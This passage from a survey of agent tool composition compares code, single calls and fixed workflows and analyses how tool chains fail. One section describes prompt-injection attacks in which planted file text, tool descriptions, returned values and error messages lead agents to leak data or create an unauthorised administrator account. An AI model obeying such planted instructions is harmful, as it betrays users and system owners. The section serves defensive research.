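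Most operations have several inputs and outputs, so two operations are more likely to fit together than a single output and a single input are. In the larger collection, an average operation could take an input from 32 others. If the connections were evenly spread, this would allow 457 × 32 × 32, or about 470,000, three-call chains out of 95 million possible three-call sequences.

An agent still has to notice these connections. About three-quarters of them joined different apps. GPT-4o mini, a small model from 2024, found the operation that could supply a missing input in about 80% of cases within one app but only 6% across apps. In a separate test of airline customer service, adding likely connections to the tools' descriptions raised the share of tasks that GPT-4o, a larger model, completed from 50% to 60%. Before the change, one agent had used a flight's departure date as the passenger's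 date of birth. Once the description named the tool that returns dates of birth, the agent called that tool.

### Questions that span sources

Dunkel uses the term Library Composition Effect for an agent's ability to answer questions that span several sources and that no tool's author foresaw. In the paper's example, an agent investigates a failing service. An alert from the monitoring system Alertmanager identifies the service. NetBox, an inventory of network equipment, shows which machine runs it, and the logs in Graylog show how it failed. A wiki page describes a possible way to recover. Xen Orchestra, which manages virtual machines, confirms the machine's state, and the cloud provider's records supply the remaining details. Once someone asks the question, the agent writes a short program to join these sources.

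A manager might similarly ask the salary agent whether the departments that pay below the industry figure also lost the most staff. The answer requires payroll data, public pay data and HR's list of leavers. If the agent has access to all three, it can answer without a tool built specifically for that question.

The effect is plausible, but Dunkel acknowledges that it is unmeasured and gives only the one example. One open question is whether agents can reliably chain three or four sources, or whether accuracy drops sharply beyond two.

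The effect also doesn't depend on DADL, since an agent connected to several ordinary MCP servers can combine them too. Tasks in MCP-Atlas, a benchmark with 36 real servers, typically take three to six calls, often to more than one server. In *Explore Separately, Adopt Selectively*, Mazhar, Maekawa and Bhutani (2026) gave three models only the tools each task needed, and the models earned 66% to 78% of the available credit. Agents can therefore often combine a few sources when they don't have to search for the tools.

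### Finding tools in a large catalogue

DADL's public catalogue has 1,833 tools, and their descriptions would take up about 142,000 tokens of a model's input. Dunkel's runtime instead gives the model two tools. `search` takes keywords and returns the signatures of a few matching tools, and `execute` runs a program that calls them. Describing these two takes about 1,000 tokens, however large the catalogue is.

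This 142-fold reduction doesn't count the tokens the agent uses to search, read the results and write programs. It also applies to the whole catalogue, but for a typical service with about 92 tools, the reduction is roughly sixfold. The figures don't measure whether `search` returns the right tools.

*Scalable LLM Agent Tool Access in the Cloud* (Li, Song and colleagues, 2026) tested that question at Alibaba Cloud. On a public benchmark, a model given every tool's description chose the correct tool 92.4% of the time from 15 tools but only 78.2% from 640. The descriptions of Alibaba's own tools no longer fitted in the model's input once there were 752 tools. The company's search combines keyword matching with embeddings, which are lists of numbers that represent a text's meaning. It reduced 3,616 tools to a shortlist of 15, which included the correct tool 98.2% of the time. The model then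 chose correctly in 81.6% of cases.

Search is less reliable for chains because people describe the result they want, not the steps to reach it. Someone who asks for a load balancer may not mention the virtual network it requires, so a search for similar descriptions finds the tool that creates the load balancer but misses the one that creates the network. With 3,616 tools, such a search found every prerequisite for only 24.5% of requests. Letting the model search again for missing tools raised this to 56.1%. When software worked out the dependencies from the tools' schemas in advance, the search returned every prerequisite for every request.

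Longer chains make the problem worse. Liu, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *PlanBench-XL*, built a catalogue of 1,665 simulated retail tools and 327 tasks that need at least five calls each. In one task, the agent has to get from a shipment to an order, a return request, an internal review, a refund and finally the time of the refund. Mazhar and colleagues added the MCP-Atlas tools to this catalogue and tested three models on 75 of the tasks:

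| Tools the agent could see | Tasks completed |
|---|---|
| Only the tools that the task needed | 76–100% |
| Top 50 results from one search | 0% |
| Top 500 results from one search | 19–31% |
| Results of repeated searches, using the best method | 23–39% |

The models could complete most of the chains but usually couldn't find the tools for them. The refund request doesn't mention an internal review, so a single search had little chance of finding the tool for that step. Mazhar and colleagues had the agent search again whenever it lacked a tool, such as one that converts a review number into a refund number. If several tools looked suitable, the agent could try each in a separate branch and keep only the useful results. This method found all the tools for a valid chain in only 83 of the 327 tasks. In those 83, GPT-6 Luna gave the correct answer 81.9% of the time.

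In the original tests by Liu and colleagues, Gemini 3.1 Pro solved 77.1% of the tasks and GPT-5.4 solved 51.9%. Their search matches tools by the types of data they take and return, so an agent can look for any tool that returns a refund time. With this search, choosing a tool became the main difficulty. In failed runs, 78% of the calls that made no progress came after the agent had already found a useful tool. The comparison with Mazhar and colleagues is rough, because they used different models and also required the agent to call every tool on a valid path, but it suggests that precise types help agents find tools as well as connect them.

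A large catalogue did less harm on MCP-Atlas, where chains are shorter. With the best search method, the three models earned 62–90% of the available credit, and two of them did better than when given only the necessary tools. Catalogue size therefore doesn't determine accuracy by itself, but other studies have found that it matters. In *ToolSearcher* (2026), every method selected tools less accurately as the library grew from 4,000 to 16,000 tools. *Beyond Static Tools* (2026) found that expanding a scientific library from 100 to 500 tools sometimes reduced accuracy. It attributes this to near-duplicates, such as two thermodynamic calculators with slightly different assumptions, which can crowd the right tool out of the search results.

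### Saving a chain as a tool

If someone saves a five-call chain as a composite tool, the agent has to find one tool instead of five. In ToolUniverse, a collection of more than 600 scientific tools, a developer can do this by writing a Python function that calls other tools, then registering it with a name, a description and an input schema.

Zitnik Lab's *Tool Composition Tutorial* describes several patterns for combining tools. One chain looks up the known drugs for a disease, finds their chemical structures and predicts whether each drug can pass from the blood into the brain. A "broadcast" sends the same query to three literature databases and has a model summarise the results. A loop tests how well a compound binds to a protein, asks a model for an improved version and repeats this up to five times. Other composites try a second tool if the first fails.

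An agent can also save its own programs. In an example by the developer krasserm, an agent writes a program that finds a GitHub user's most popular repositories and lists their latest commits. Once the program works, the agent's own user asks it to save the program as a function, with the GitHub username and the numbers of repositories and commits as parameters. The agent stores the function's signature separately from its code, so a later agent can decide whether to use the function without reading the code. The salary agent could save its work as `pay_report` in the same way, with the department and the address of the public data as parameters.

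GitHub Next's *Agent Functions* proposes a shared registry for such functions. Each entry defines a task by its input and output types, the permissions it needs and the tests that any implementation must pass. A planning agent looks for suitable functions and has another agent write any that are missing. Each function runs in a small virtual machine that enforces its permissions, and users can save a successful workflow as a new function. In one example, five functions read a public bug report, remove unsafe content, classify the report, draft a reply and post it. Only the function that posts the reply has write access, and the agent that coordinates them never reads the report. This is still a proposal, and GitHub Next gives no results.

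### New abilities and lower costs

A composite tool can reach only the data and services that its primitive calls can reach. `pay_report` saves work, but an agent with the same underlying tools could produce the report without it. Connecting the HR system adds a new ability, because no chain could reach the list of leavers before. Searching the library also makes new tasks possible when it holds too many tools for the model to see at once.

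A composite can still add an ability if the agent can't write the same steps itself. For instance, SPA plans don't support arithmetic, so an SPA planner can't calculate a median salary, but it can call a saved tool that does.

Saving tools might also help an agent finish tasks that it would otherwise get wrong, since models can lose track of information in long runs. Chen, Gai and colleagues (2026), in *SkillCraft*, tested this on 126 tasks by letting agents save working chains as code and reuse them. Four of the eight models show the range of results:

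| Model | Success without saved tools | Success with saved tools | Change in tokens |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.2 | 87% | 90% | −79% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 94% | 96% | −71% |
| GLM-4.7 | 72% | 86% | −39% |
| Kimi K2 Thinking | 44% | 44% | −42% |

For the strongest models, saved tools mainly reduced the tokens used on tasks they could already do. Weaker models can also complete more tasks with saved tools. GLM-4.7 completed 17 more, although Kimi completed only one more. The tasks favoured reuse because each repeated the same steps for three to five items. The agents without saved tools made their calls one at a time, so some of the token savings probably came from running code rather than from reuse.

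Building saved tools on top of other saved tools lowered GPT-5.2's task completion rate from 90% to 79%. The quality of the saved code also mattered. On eight hard tasks, Chen and colleagues gave four models one another's tools. All four completed every task with Claude's tools and used 54–81% fewer tokens. With MiniMax's tools, token use ranged from 18% lower to 48% higher.

*SkillsBench* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2026) studied a broader kind of reuse, based on "skills", which are packages of written instructions, sometimes with scripts. Skills selected by experts raised the average success rate from 33.9% to 50.5% across 18 combinations of model and agent software. When agents wrote their own skills before starting a task, the success rate was 8 to 12 percentage points lower than with no skills. Some agents never found the skills they had written, and some skills contained mistakes stated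 confidently.

These results suggest that an agent should test a procedure before adding it to a library. They don't necessarily conflict with *SkillCraft*, where agents saved code only after it had worked. *What Keeps Agent Skills from Being Reusable?* (2026) cites research showing that even good packages help less reliably when agents have to find them among 34,000 others.

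## Single calls, code and fixed workflows in experiments

Most of the early figures for code composition came from companies that sell it. In 2026, several research groups compared the designs by giving the same models the same tasks and changing how the models combined tools. Code usually needed fewer turns and tokens. Its effect on accuracy depended on the model, the structure of the task and how well the tools' outputs were documented.

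### Fourteen models and tools that echo

Patel, Sen and colleagues (2026), in *The Bitter Lesson of Tool Calling*, tested 14 Anthropic and OpenAI models on 309 items from BFCL v4, a standard benchmark of tool calling. Each item has a request, a set of functions and a list of required calls. The models answered once with ordinary tool calls and once with a Python script that called typed stubs. An answer counted as correct only if it contained every required call with the right arguments.

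Code matched or beat single calls for 11 of the 14 models, but the average over all 14 was slightly lower with code:

| Model | Single calls | Code |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 73.5% | 84.1% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 80.9% | 87.4% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 84.8% | 84.8% |
| GPT-4.1 | 81.9% | 62.1% |
| GPT-5.4 mini | 79.3% | 55.0% |
| GPT-4o | 81.9% | 55.0% |
| Average of all 14 | 78.6% | 77.0% |

The three models that did worse with code all wrote a backslash and the letter n where a script needed a line break, so Python rejected any script longer than one line. Without these models, the averages are 82.3% for code and 78.0% for single calls. In ordinary use, an agent would see the error message and could correct its script, but the experiment allowed only one attempt.

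Patel and colleagues conclude that a model's success with code depends on its generation. But GPT-5.4 mini, from March 2026, made the mistake and the older GPT-5 nano, from August 2025, did not, so age can't be the whole explanation.

A second test had 52 tasks that each required 2 to 20 calls in sequence. Code scored 18.8 points higher than single calls on chains of 12 or more calls, but over all lengths seven models did worse with code, six did better and one did the same. With code, Claude Haiku 4.5 fell from 88.5% to 73.1%, Claude Sonnet 4.5 from 90.4% to 88.5%, and GPT-5.6 Sol from 96.2% to 90.4%, while Claude Sonnet 5 rose from 80.8% to 96.2%. The three declines contradict Patel and colleagues' statement that all five Anthropic models and the three GPT-5.6 models at least matched single calls in every additional test. With only 52 tasks, most of the smaller differences could be chance.

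A more serious weakness of the chain test is that its tools only returned their arguments. In one task, the model had to find the circumference of a circle with a radius of 7 and use it as the side of a square. Its script called the circumference tool, but then calculated 2π × 7 separately and passed that number to the square tool instead of the first call's output. The model could do this because it knew the formula, but a salary agent can't work out what is in a spreadsheet it hasn't opened. The test therefore measures whether models write the right calls in the right order, not whether they can use real results. Patel and colleagues acknowledge that their findings may not transfer to tasks in which one call's output affects the next.

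This weakness matters less for independent calls. In 32 tasks, the models had to make between 7 and 48 separate calls, such as looking up the population of each country on a list. Ten models made every call, whether they used single calls or code. GPT-5 completed 71.9% of the tasks with single calls and 96.9% with code. Claude Sonnet 5 completed 70 single calls but never a set of 100, though GPT-5.6 Sol did. With code, Claude Sonnet 5 made all 100, because a loop over 100 items is no harder to write than a loop over ten. Code used more tokens than single calls below about 26 calls because its instructions were longer, but at 48 calls it used 3,535 tokens, compared with 5,097 for single calls.

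The last test repeated 31 tasks with 128 tool schemas in the model's input instead of only the relevant ones. The average score fell by 2.3 points with single calls and rose by 5.5 points with code. Nearly all the gain with code came from the three models with the line-break problem, and the other 11 gained an average of only 0.6 points, so the rise is weak evidence that code copes better with irrelevant schemas. Single calls still had the higher average with 128 schemas, 81.3% against 78.1%.

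### Real servers and the shape of the task

Felendler and colleagues used tools that return real data, connecting agents to 10 MCP servers for services such as unit conversion, scientific computing, Wikipedia and Reddit. GPT-4o, GPT-4.1 and GPT-4.1 mini each attempted 34 tasks with both designs. Twenty tasks needed one server, ten needed two and four needed three.

An agent often took dozens of turns with single calls, but usually finished after one or two program runs with code. Code also used fewer tokens and less time on average, and the savings grew with the number of servers. A few code runs were unusually slow, mainly because the agent spent a long time searching the servers for suitable tools.

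Quality was similar on most tasks. Code did worse on some three-server tasks because the program lacked a necessary branch or was based on a wrong assumption about the whole task. An agent making single calls could sometimes recover from such a mistake on the next turn.

Felendler and colleagues attribute the differences mainly to the shape of the graph of calls, not to the model. Both designs completed straight chains, but code did so more efficiently. Code also suited tasks in which one result leads to many independent calls, because a program can run them in parallel and combine the results. Single calls worked better when the agent had to judge a result before continuing, such as when choosing relevant Reddit threads or rewording a search. The salary agent is therefore better suited to using code to fetch benchmarks for 30 departments and single calls to decide whether a web page describes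 comparable jobs.

Four three-server tasks are too few to show how often code fails on complicated work. The three models were also old when the study appeared in February 2026, and the judges that scored the results ran on one of them, GPT-4o.

Another experiment found a similar pattern after training models for each design. Du, Zhou and colleagues (2026), in *HyperTool*, trained two open models, Qwen3-8B and Qwen3-32B, to make single calls, and trained separate copies to write blocks of code. Both kinds of training used the same tasks and the same teacher model. On MCP-Universe, a benchmark with real MCP servers, the results were:

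| Model and task area | Single calls | Code |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-8B, all tasks | 20.9% | 33.3% |
| Qwen3-8B, financial analysis | 32.5% | 62.5% |
| Qwen3-8B, web search | 16.0% | 18.0% |
| Qwen3-32B, all tasks | 24.2% | 35.3% |

The difference between the two areas fits what Felendler and colleagues observed, since financial questions often require an agent to combine and calculate figures, whereas web search requires it to judge pages. With code, the smaller model also made more primitive calls in fewer turns, averaging 47.6 calls in 21.8 turns, compared with 26.9 calls in 28.8 turns without it.

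When agents used code, the share of failures in which they answered too early rose from 29.8% to 54.9%. Part of this rise came from other errors becoming rarer. But Du and colleagues suggest that a short result can also make a model overconfident, so that it skips a needed check. For example, if a salary agent's program reads last year's spreadsheet and returns only "4% below the industry median", the agent has no reason to suspect the mistake.

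They tell their agents not to group calls when the next step depends on the meaning of a result, or when the form of a result matters but is unknown. An agent can still use the code interface in these cases by writing a block with a single call. About 44% of the blocks had only one call.

Code may make little difference when an agent already has flexible tools. Yang, Yu and Desell (2026), in *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?*, compared three sets of tools for the coding agents Claude Code and Codex. One set contained only a tool for running code. On calculation tasks and software bugs, pass rates with the three sets stayed within three percentage points of each other. Cost varied more:

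| Agent and task | Cost with only the code tool, against the cheapest alternative |
|---|---|
| Claude Code, calculations | 24.6% lower |
| Codex, calculations | 6.7% lower (could be chance) |
| Codex, software bugs | 19.9% lower |
| Claude Code, software bugs | 14.4% higher (could be chance) |

The extra cost for Claude Code came mostly from bugs it failed to fix in at least some attempts. These agents were replacing their own tools for reading and editing files, not connecting outside services, so the results are weaker evidence about chains like the salary report.

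### What a program needs to know about its tools

A program depends on the form of each tool's result. For example, the ten-line salary program uses `pay.text` and would fail if `read_file` returned a list of rows. *Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) measured how much it helps to tell the model what each tool returns.

The study tested three open-weight models in a simulated workplace with 42 tools on 12 servers. The 119 tasks included adding up invoices, following a record through several systems and making a change only if a condition held. Software, rather than another model, checked whether each task succeeded by examining the final state of the workplace. Rai committed to the main analysis before running the test, which prevents choosing the most favorable comparison afterwards.

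In one version of code composition, each stub included a handwritten description of its result, such as field names and types. In the other, each stub gave only the result's basic type, a dictionary or a list.

| Model | Single calls | Code with results described | Code without descriptions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8 27B | 85.7% | 99.2% | 97.5% |
| Gemma 4 26B | 86.6% | 89.1% | 66.4% |
| Nemotron 3 Nano 30B | 36.1% | 55.5% | 16.0% |

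The descriptions determined which design did better for Gemma and Nemotron, but made little difference for Qwen. Rai points out that earlier comparisons may have measured the quality of the stubs rather than the agents' ability. The result also gives server developers a reason to declare output schemas. However, the author wrote the descriptions and tuned them on practice tasks from the same templates, and nobody has tested whether ordinary output schemas help as much.

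Code with descriptions used 70% to 90% fewer tokens than single calls. Some of that saving came from loading fewer tool schemas, because the code agents searched for tools while the single-call agents received all 42 schemas. A fairer comparison gave both designs the same short list, usually two or three tools that a small model had selected:

| Model | Success with single calls | Success with code | Tokens saved by code |
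|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8 27B | 82.4% | 98.3% | 62% |
| Gemma 4 26B | 86.6% | 93.3% | 62% |
| Nemotron 3 Nano 30B | 56.3% | 67.2% | 72% |

Code still did better, though these agents could fall back on single calls, and Nemotron did so in 13.4% of runs. The 119 tasks came from only 21 templates, so they provide less evidence than 119 unrelated tasks would. Once Rai allowed for this, code's advantage on a combined score of success, tokens and time was statistically clear only for Qwen.

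Rai had expected the short list to improve code composition as well, but the study found no clear benefit over letting the code agent search for tools itself, even after the number of tasks was doubled to 238. The selection step helped the two weaker models slightly and slowed the strongest one.

In a smaller test with 10 tasks, Qwen completed nine with code when the catalogue had 2,000 tools. It completed none with single calls, because the schemas no longer fitted in its input. This result shows the value of search more than that of code. All the simulated tools responded instantly, and Rai turned off the models' extended reasoning, so the times and success rates may not carry over to real servers.

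### Workflows fixed in advance

When the model composes tool calls in code, it can rewrite a program that fails. In a fixed workflow, the model or a developer sets the steps once, and software then runs them on every new input.

Liu, Huang and colleagues (2026), in *AgentOrch*, compared this approach with single calls on 650 business procedures. Each procedure had several variants with different inputs and errors, making 3,220 variants in total. In the first design, a model wrote one workflow, including branches and loops, from a description of the procedure, and software ran it on every variant without using the model again. In the second, the model handled each variant one tool call at a time. Both designs used the same 64 simulated tools for services such as Slack, Salesforce and Google Sheets.

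Single calls were more accurate for every model, but the gap was much smaller for recent ones:

| Model | Lead of single calls over a fixed workflow |
|---|---|
| GPT-3.5 Turbo | 40.7 points |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 15.1 points |
| Claude Opus 5 | 8.5 points |

To reach this accuracy, single calls required an average of 23 times as many model calls per procedure across three of the models. The accuracy of written workflows rose by an average of 10 points when the model added one step at a time and software checked the form of each addition. In a separate test, accuracy rose by about 6 points when the model revised its workflow after seeing how it had run. The improvement was almost the same on variants that weren't used in the revision. A company that produces the same pay report every month could therefore test and correct a workflow before relying on it.

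Two features of the experiment may exaggerate the gap. The single-call agent saw the inputs and the results, while the workflow's author saw neither. The accuracy score also measures agreement with a reference run, including the order of calls, so a workflow could score lower for taking a different but valid route. Otani and colleagues found no clear gap on lookup questions, where agents could revise a failed plan. The size of the gap probably depends on how much a procedure varies between runs.

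Lim, Sharudin and colleagues (2026), in *Declarative Skills for AI Agents in Knowledge-Grounded Tool-Use Workflows*, tested a workflow that fixed the phases of a task, not the individual calls. Their agents handled 97 customer-service tasks at a simulated bank. They had to verify the customer's identity, follow the bank's written procedures and change its records. The experiment compared three agents:

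- a plain agent that made single calls;
- the same agent with about 4,600 tokens of written instructions;
- an agent that software moved through phases such as verification, planning and execution, with only certain tools available in each.

The written instructions that Lim and colleagues call "declarative" are advice to the model, unlike the plans that SPA checks. Nothing enforces the instructions, and they don't specify a sequence of calls.

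Five models attempted the tasks, first with the relevant bank documents supplied and then with a search tool for finding them. Overall, the written instructions made no difference. In 73 cases only the agent with instructions succeeded, and in 71 only the plain agent did. But the plain agent did better when the documents were supplied, by 49 cases to 36, and the agent with instructions did better when it had to search, by 37 to 22. Lim and colleagues infer that instructions help when they supply information the agent would otherwise lack, and can distract it when it already has what it needs.

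The instructions made individual changes to the bank's records more accurate in all ten combinations of model and document access. Overall success didn't rise with accuracy, because a typical task required about eight changes and one mistake was enough to fail it.

The agent with fixed phases did much worse than the plain agent. In 132 cases only the plain agent succeeded, compared with 46 where only the agent with fixed phases did. With the documents supplied, DeepSeek V4 Pro's success rate fell from 46.2% to 20.0%. The phases also usually made tasks more expensive, partly because the agent kept retrying failed calls. The experiment tested only one design on one kind of work, with a single run per task, and a better set of phases might do less harm.

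### Putting the condition on the tool

Lim and colleagues added the phases partly to prevent unauthorised writes, changes made to the bank's records before the agent has verified the customer. The phases didn't help with DeepSeek V4 Pro. The software checked the agent's phase, not the call itself, so an unauthorised write could go through when the software had assigned the wrong phase.

They then removed the phases and put the same condition on the tools. If the agent tried to change a record before verifying the customer, the software blocked the call and returned an instruction to verify first.

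| Agent | Tasks with an unauthorised write | Tasks completed | Cost per task |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain | 4.3% | 46.2% | $0.009 |
| Fixed phases | 4.4% | 20.0% | $0.016 |
| Plain, with the condition on the tools | 0% | 49.0% | $0.022 |

With the condition on the tools, none of the agent's 467 writes came before verification. A correctly written check guarantees this, so the more informative finding is that the agent still completed as many tasks. It cost more than twice as much as the plain agent, partly because some conversations became longer. Lim and colleagues tried the check on only one model, with the documents supplied. The check also covers only one condition and doesn't establish whether a verified customer asked for the change.

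Written instructions are a weaker safeguard. With them, Claude Haiku 4.5 made an unauthorised write in 15.6% of tasks, down from 41.7%. Its success rate also fell, from 25.0% to 15.6%.

The rate of unauthorised writes depends on the simulated customer as well as the agent. Qwen3.5 Flash made unauthorised writes in 32.0% of tasks when GPT-4o mini played the customer, but in 10.4% when DeepSeek V4 Pro did. Comparing two agents' safety is therefore unreliable unless both face the same simulated customer.

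### Attacks on the two designs

Felendler and colleagues also tested whether code gives attackers more opportunities. They built a database server that recorded who could open which doors, then made one part of it hostile in each of four attacks on GPT-4o and GPT-4.1:

| What the attacker controlled | What the agent did | Designs affected, according to the study |
|---|---|---|
| A file that the agent read while looking for tools | reversed the user's query, listing people without access | both |
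| A tool's description | repeated steps that could never succeed | both |
| A value that a tool returned | answered with another person's data | code only |
| The text of an error message | created an unauthorised administrator account | code only |

Both models were vulnerable. None of the attacks had to break out of the sandbox, because the program used tools it had permission to use. In the second attack, the code agent kept rewriting its program automatically, whereas a person supervising single calls could intervene between attempts.

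The label "code only" is doubtful for the last two attacks. In the third, the tool returned the wrong person's passkey. Nothing in a passkey shows whose it is, so a model making single calls would probably also copy it into the next call. In the fourth, the code agent read an instruction in the error message and followed it in its next program. Felendler and colleagues argue that an agent making single calls treats an error only as feedback, but that agent also reads the message and could follow the instruction by calling the same tools one at a time. The study doesn't report success rates for each attack under each design, which would be needed to settle this.

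Rai found no increase in risk from code in a small pilot. Instructions planted in tool results succeeded in 14.8% of 108 runs with single calls and 9.3% of 108 runs with code, a difference that could easily be chance. The pilot used one model and six tasks, and only one style of attack worked. No attack succeeded when a small model had cut the list of available tools to two or three, mostly because this removed the tools the attacker needed.

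The model that selects the tools then becomes a target itself. In another test, Rai added a hostile tool whose description included an instruction to select it for every task. A general-purpose model selected it in all 39 tasks. Two milder descriptions never worked. A short list can limit the damage from an attack, but a developer shouldn't treat it as a decision about what the agent is allowed to do.

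Felendler and colleagues propose several layers of defence for code. Software checks the program for dangerous operations before it runs, and a sandbox limits its resources. A separate model looks for hidden instructions in tool descriptions beforehand and in results and error messages afterwards. This combination blocked all four attacks in every trial, but the researchers didn't test it against an attacker who knew about the defences.

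### Which tasks suit which design

The experiments support different designs for different parts of a job:

| Structure of the task | Design with the most support | Salary example |
|---|---|---|
| One or two calls | single calls | sending a finished summary |
| Next step depends on judging a result | single calls | deciding whether public pay data covers similar jobs |
| Many independent calls | code | fetching benchmarks for 30 departments |
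| Predictable steps with documented results | code | calculating medians and matching them to benchmarks |
| The same procedure, repeated often | a workflow written once and tested | producing the report every month |

The evidence for using code is strongest when a task needs many independent calls. Code made these calls more reliable for some models and cheaper beyond a few dozen calls, and the studies of real servers found the same. The evidence is weaker for long sequential chains, because the chains that Patel and colleagues tested passed no data between calls and Rai simulated the tools. For repeated procedures, a fixed workflow needs far fewer model calls but is somewhat less accurate, so it makes most sense where software or a person can catch the runs that go wrong.

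Most real jobs combine several of these structures, and OpenAI advises mixing code with direct calls. But in the one direct test of offering both interfaces, by Du and colleagues, Qwen3-8B completed 26.9% of tasks when it could choose between ordinary calls and code blocks, compared with 33.3% when it had only code blocks. A stronger model might choose better. A developer can also choose the interface for each tool in advance.

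## How chains fail without an attacker

A chain can fail without an attacker because any call in it can go wrong. If each step succeeds 95% of the time and errors are independent, a ten-step chain succeeds about 60% of the time (0.95¹⁰) and a 20-step chain about 36%.

In general, if each step succeeds with probability *p*, a chain of *t* steps succeeds with probability *p*ᵗ. Sinha, Arun and colleagues (2025), in *The Illusion of Diminishing Returns*, turn this around to find the length *H* at which a chain's success rate falls to *s*:

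*H* = ln *s* / ln *p*

For a success rate of 50%, *H* is about 14 steps when *p* is 95%, 69 steps when it is 99%, and 693 steps when it is 99.9%. Raising *p* from 99% to 99.9% therefore allows chains ten times as long, even though the difference looks small in a test of single calls.

The formula assumes that *p* stays the same throughout, that one error doesn't affect the chance of another, and that the agent never corrects a mistake, but none of these assumptions holds for real agents.

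### Why errors are not independent

Suppose each of ten steps in a chain fails 5% of the time, all for the same reason, such as an expired password for the payroll system. The steps then fail in the same runs, so the chain succeeds 95% of the time. If instead no run ever contains two failures, half of all runs contain one, and the chain succeeds only 50% of the time. A developer therefore can't work out how often the chain succeeds from the success rates of its steps alone.

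Wan, Nourian and colleagues (2026), in *APIFlow-Bench*, measured the gap with simulated web services at the software company Postman. Each task opens with something broken, such as a request that fails because its access token has expired, and the tasks build up into chains of as many as 20 subtasks. Nineteen models completed 93% of single subtasks. Multiplying the success rates for single subtasks predicts that the models would complete 41% of the 20-subtask chains, but they completed 74%. (This leaves out two of the 11 chains, which no model completed. With those two, the figure is 61%.)

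Part of the gap comes from the grading, which checks only the last subtask and the earlier ones it depends on. The rest probably comes from correlated errors, since a model that completes the start of a chain correctly tends to complete the later steps correctly too.

Errors can also make later errors more likely. Sinha and colleagues had models look up numbers and keep a running total, then planted mistakes in the record of the models' earlier answers. The more mistakes the record contained, the less accurate the next answers were. Larger models had the same weakness, but models that reason before answering largely avoided it.

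A model can carry an earlier mistake forward even if it makes no new ones. *Dude, Where's My State?* (Mehrotra, Tiwari and colleagues, 2026) analyses a 64-step task in which an agent had to keep adding up earlier results. The agent answered wrongly at 19 steps because a result it needed was no longer available. Another 26 answers were wrong only because they used those bad results, and none came from faulty arithmetic. Similarly, if the salary agent misreads the median, the comparison, the summary and the email will all be wrong.

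### How retries and checks change the sum

Suppose a check catches a fraction *c* of failed steps, and the agent then tries once more with the same chance of success. Each step now succeeds with probability

*p* + (1 − *p*)*cp*

If each step succeeds 95% of the time, a ten-step chain succeeds about 60% of the time. Checking each step and retrying it once when the check finds a failure raises this to about 98% if the check catches every failure, or 77% if it catches only half. The gain disappears if the second attempt fails for the same reason as the first, for example because the model misreads the same column again.

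Jin, Yu and colleagues (2026), in *Harness Engineering in LLM Tool Use via Agent-Native Reusable Tool Primitives*, tested how replanning affected a system whose planner and verifier both ran on the small model Qwen3-8B. Without replanning, the system got the right answer on 33% of tasks that required chains. One round of replanning raised this to 49%, two to 68% and three to 75%, but five rounds did no better than three.

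Voting is another way to correct errors. In *Solving a Million-Step LLM Task with Zero Errors* (2025), a model answers each small step repeatedly until one answer leads by a set number of votes. The required lead grows with the logarithm of the number of steps, so doubling a chain's length adds only a small fixed amount to the required lead. Voting relies on wrong answers varying between attempts. It also requires steps that the agent can safely repeat, such as calculating a median, rather than actions like sending an email.

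For actions that an agent can't repeat, consistency matters more than eventual success. Given five attempts at each of Wan and colleagues' tasks, models completed 85% to 92% of the tasks at least once, but completed only 42% to 86% on every attempt.

### Eight kinds of failure

The salary report could fail in any of these ways:

| Failure | Example |
|---|---|
| Missing function | The agent calls `read_spreadsheet`, but the tool's name is `read_file`. |
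| Wrong arguments | The email has no recipient, or goes to the wrong list. |
| Wrong order | The agent sends the email and then asks for approval. |
| Value not yet obtained | The agent writes the comparison before fetching the public pay data, using a made-up figure. |
| Well-typed but wrong value | The web page gives monthly pay, and the agent compares it with annual salaries. |
| Missed branch | One department has no benchmark, and the program has no step for that case. |
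| Changed interface | The payroll service renames its `salary` field, or stops including bonuses in it. |
| Stopped after some effects | The connection drops after 29 of 50 emails. |

Agents recover more easily from failures that produce an error message. In Wan and colleagues' tests, models passed 92% of tasks that required repairing a rejected request and 81% of tasks that required choosing among similar endpoints, again excluding the chains that no model completed. Some of the wrong endpoints returned plausible data instead of an error. For example, an outdated endpoint gave different numbers from its replacement, and another gave a rounded figure.

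Old results can cause the same problem. *LongDS-Bench* (2026), a benchmark of long data analyses, includes cases where an agent keeps using a table or score after the definition behind it has changed. The next call can still accept the table because its form is correct.

Missed branches can waste a whole run. *Dependable Long-Horizon LLM Agents* (Wang, Wen and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent in a simulated company that had to ask a colleague, Alex Turner, where to find some code. The agent renamed the account it was using to "Alex Turner", sent the question to somebody else and waited 81 turns for a reply without checking whether the message had reached the right person.

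### NESTFUL and nested calls

*NESTFUL* (Basu, Abdelaziz and colleagues, 2024), an early test of chains by IBM researchers, contains more than 1,800 tasks, mostly mathematical word problems. One asks for the radius of a circle that covers half of a square poster 3.4 feet wide. The answer takes four calls, which find the square's area, halve it, divide the result by π and take the square root. The model has to write the whole sequence in advance, labelling each result so that later calls can refer to it.

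GPT-4o, the best model at the time, reproduced the reference sequence exactly in 28% of tasks and reached the right answer in 60%. The second figure is higher partly because some problems have more than one valid solution. The leading models did well when a single call depended on another, but success fell sharply once the longest run of dependencies reached two. They also had more trouble when one call needed the results of two others, as `summarize` does in the salary report. Models often passed the wrong label or ignored the type of an earlier result.

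Jin and colleagues tested later models on the same tasks:

| Model | Exact sequence | Right answer |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o (2024) | 28% | 60% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 40% | 65% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 41% | 67% |
| GPT-5.4 | 42% | 68% |
| Jin and colleagues' system, with replanning | 47% | 79% |

The newer models improved less on NESTFUL than their progress on other tests might suggest. NESTFUL measures how well a model can plan a whole chain of calls without seeing any results, which is harder than what most agents do. Jin and colleagues' system, by contrast, could check its work and try again.

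### A benchmark with adjustable dependency graphs

NESTFUL's tasks come from public datasets, so models may have seen them in training. Its authors also couldn't vary one source of difficulty while holding the others constant. Maekawa, Hassell and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Reliable Benchmarking*, addressed both problems with FuncBenchGen, a program that invents new functions for every task. It works in four steps:

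1. It creates a line of functions in which each one needs the output of the one before. The number of links in this line is the depth of the graph.
2. It adds the other required functions, each of which supplies an input to a function already in the graph.
3. It adds irrelevant functions. Some accept the output of a required function, so they look useful, while others have no connection to the required ones.
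4. It gives each function a random name, such as `func_yep`, and a schema with typed inputs and an output.

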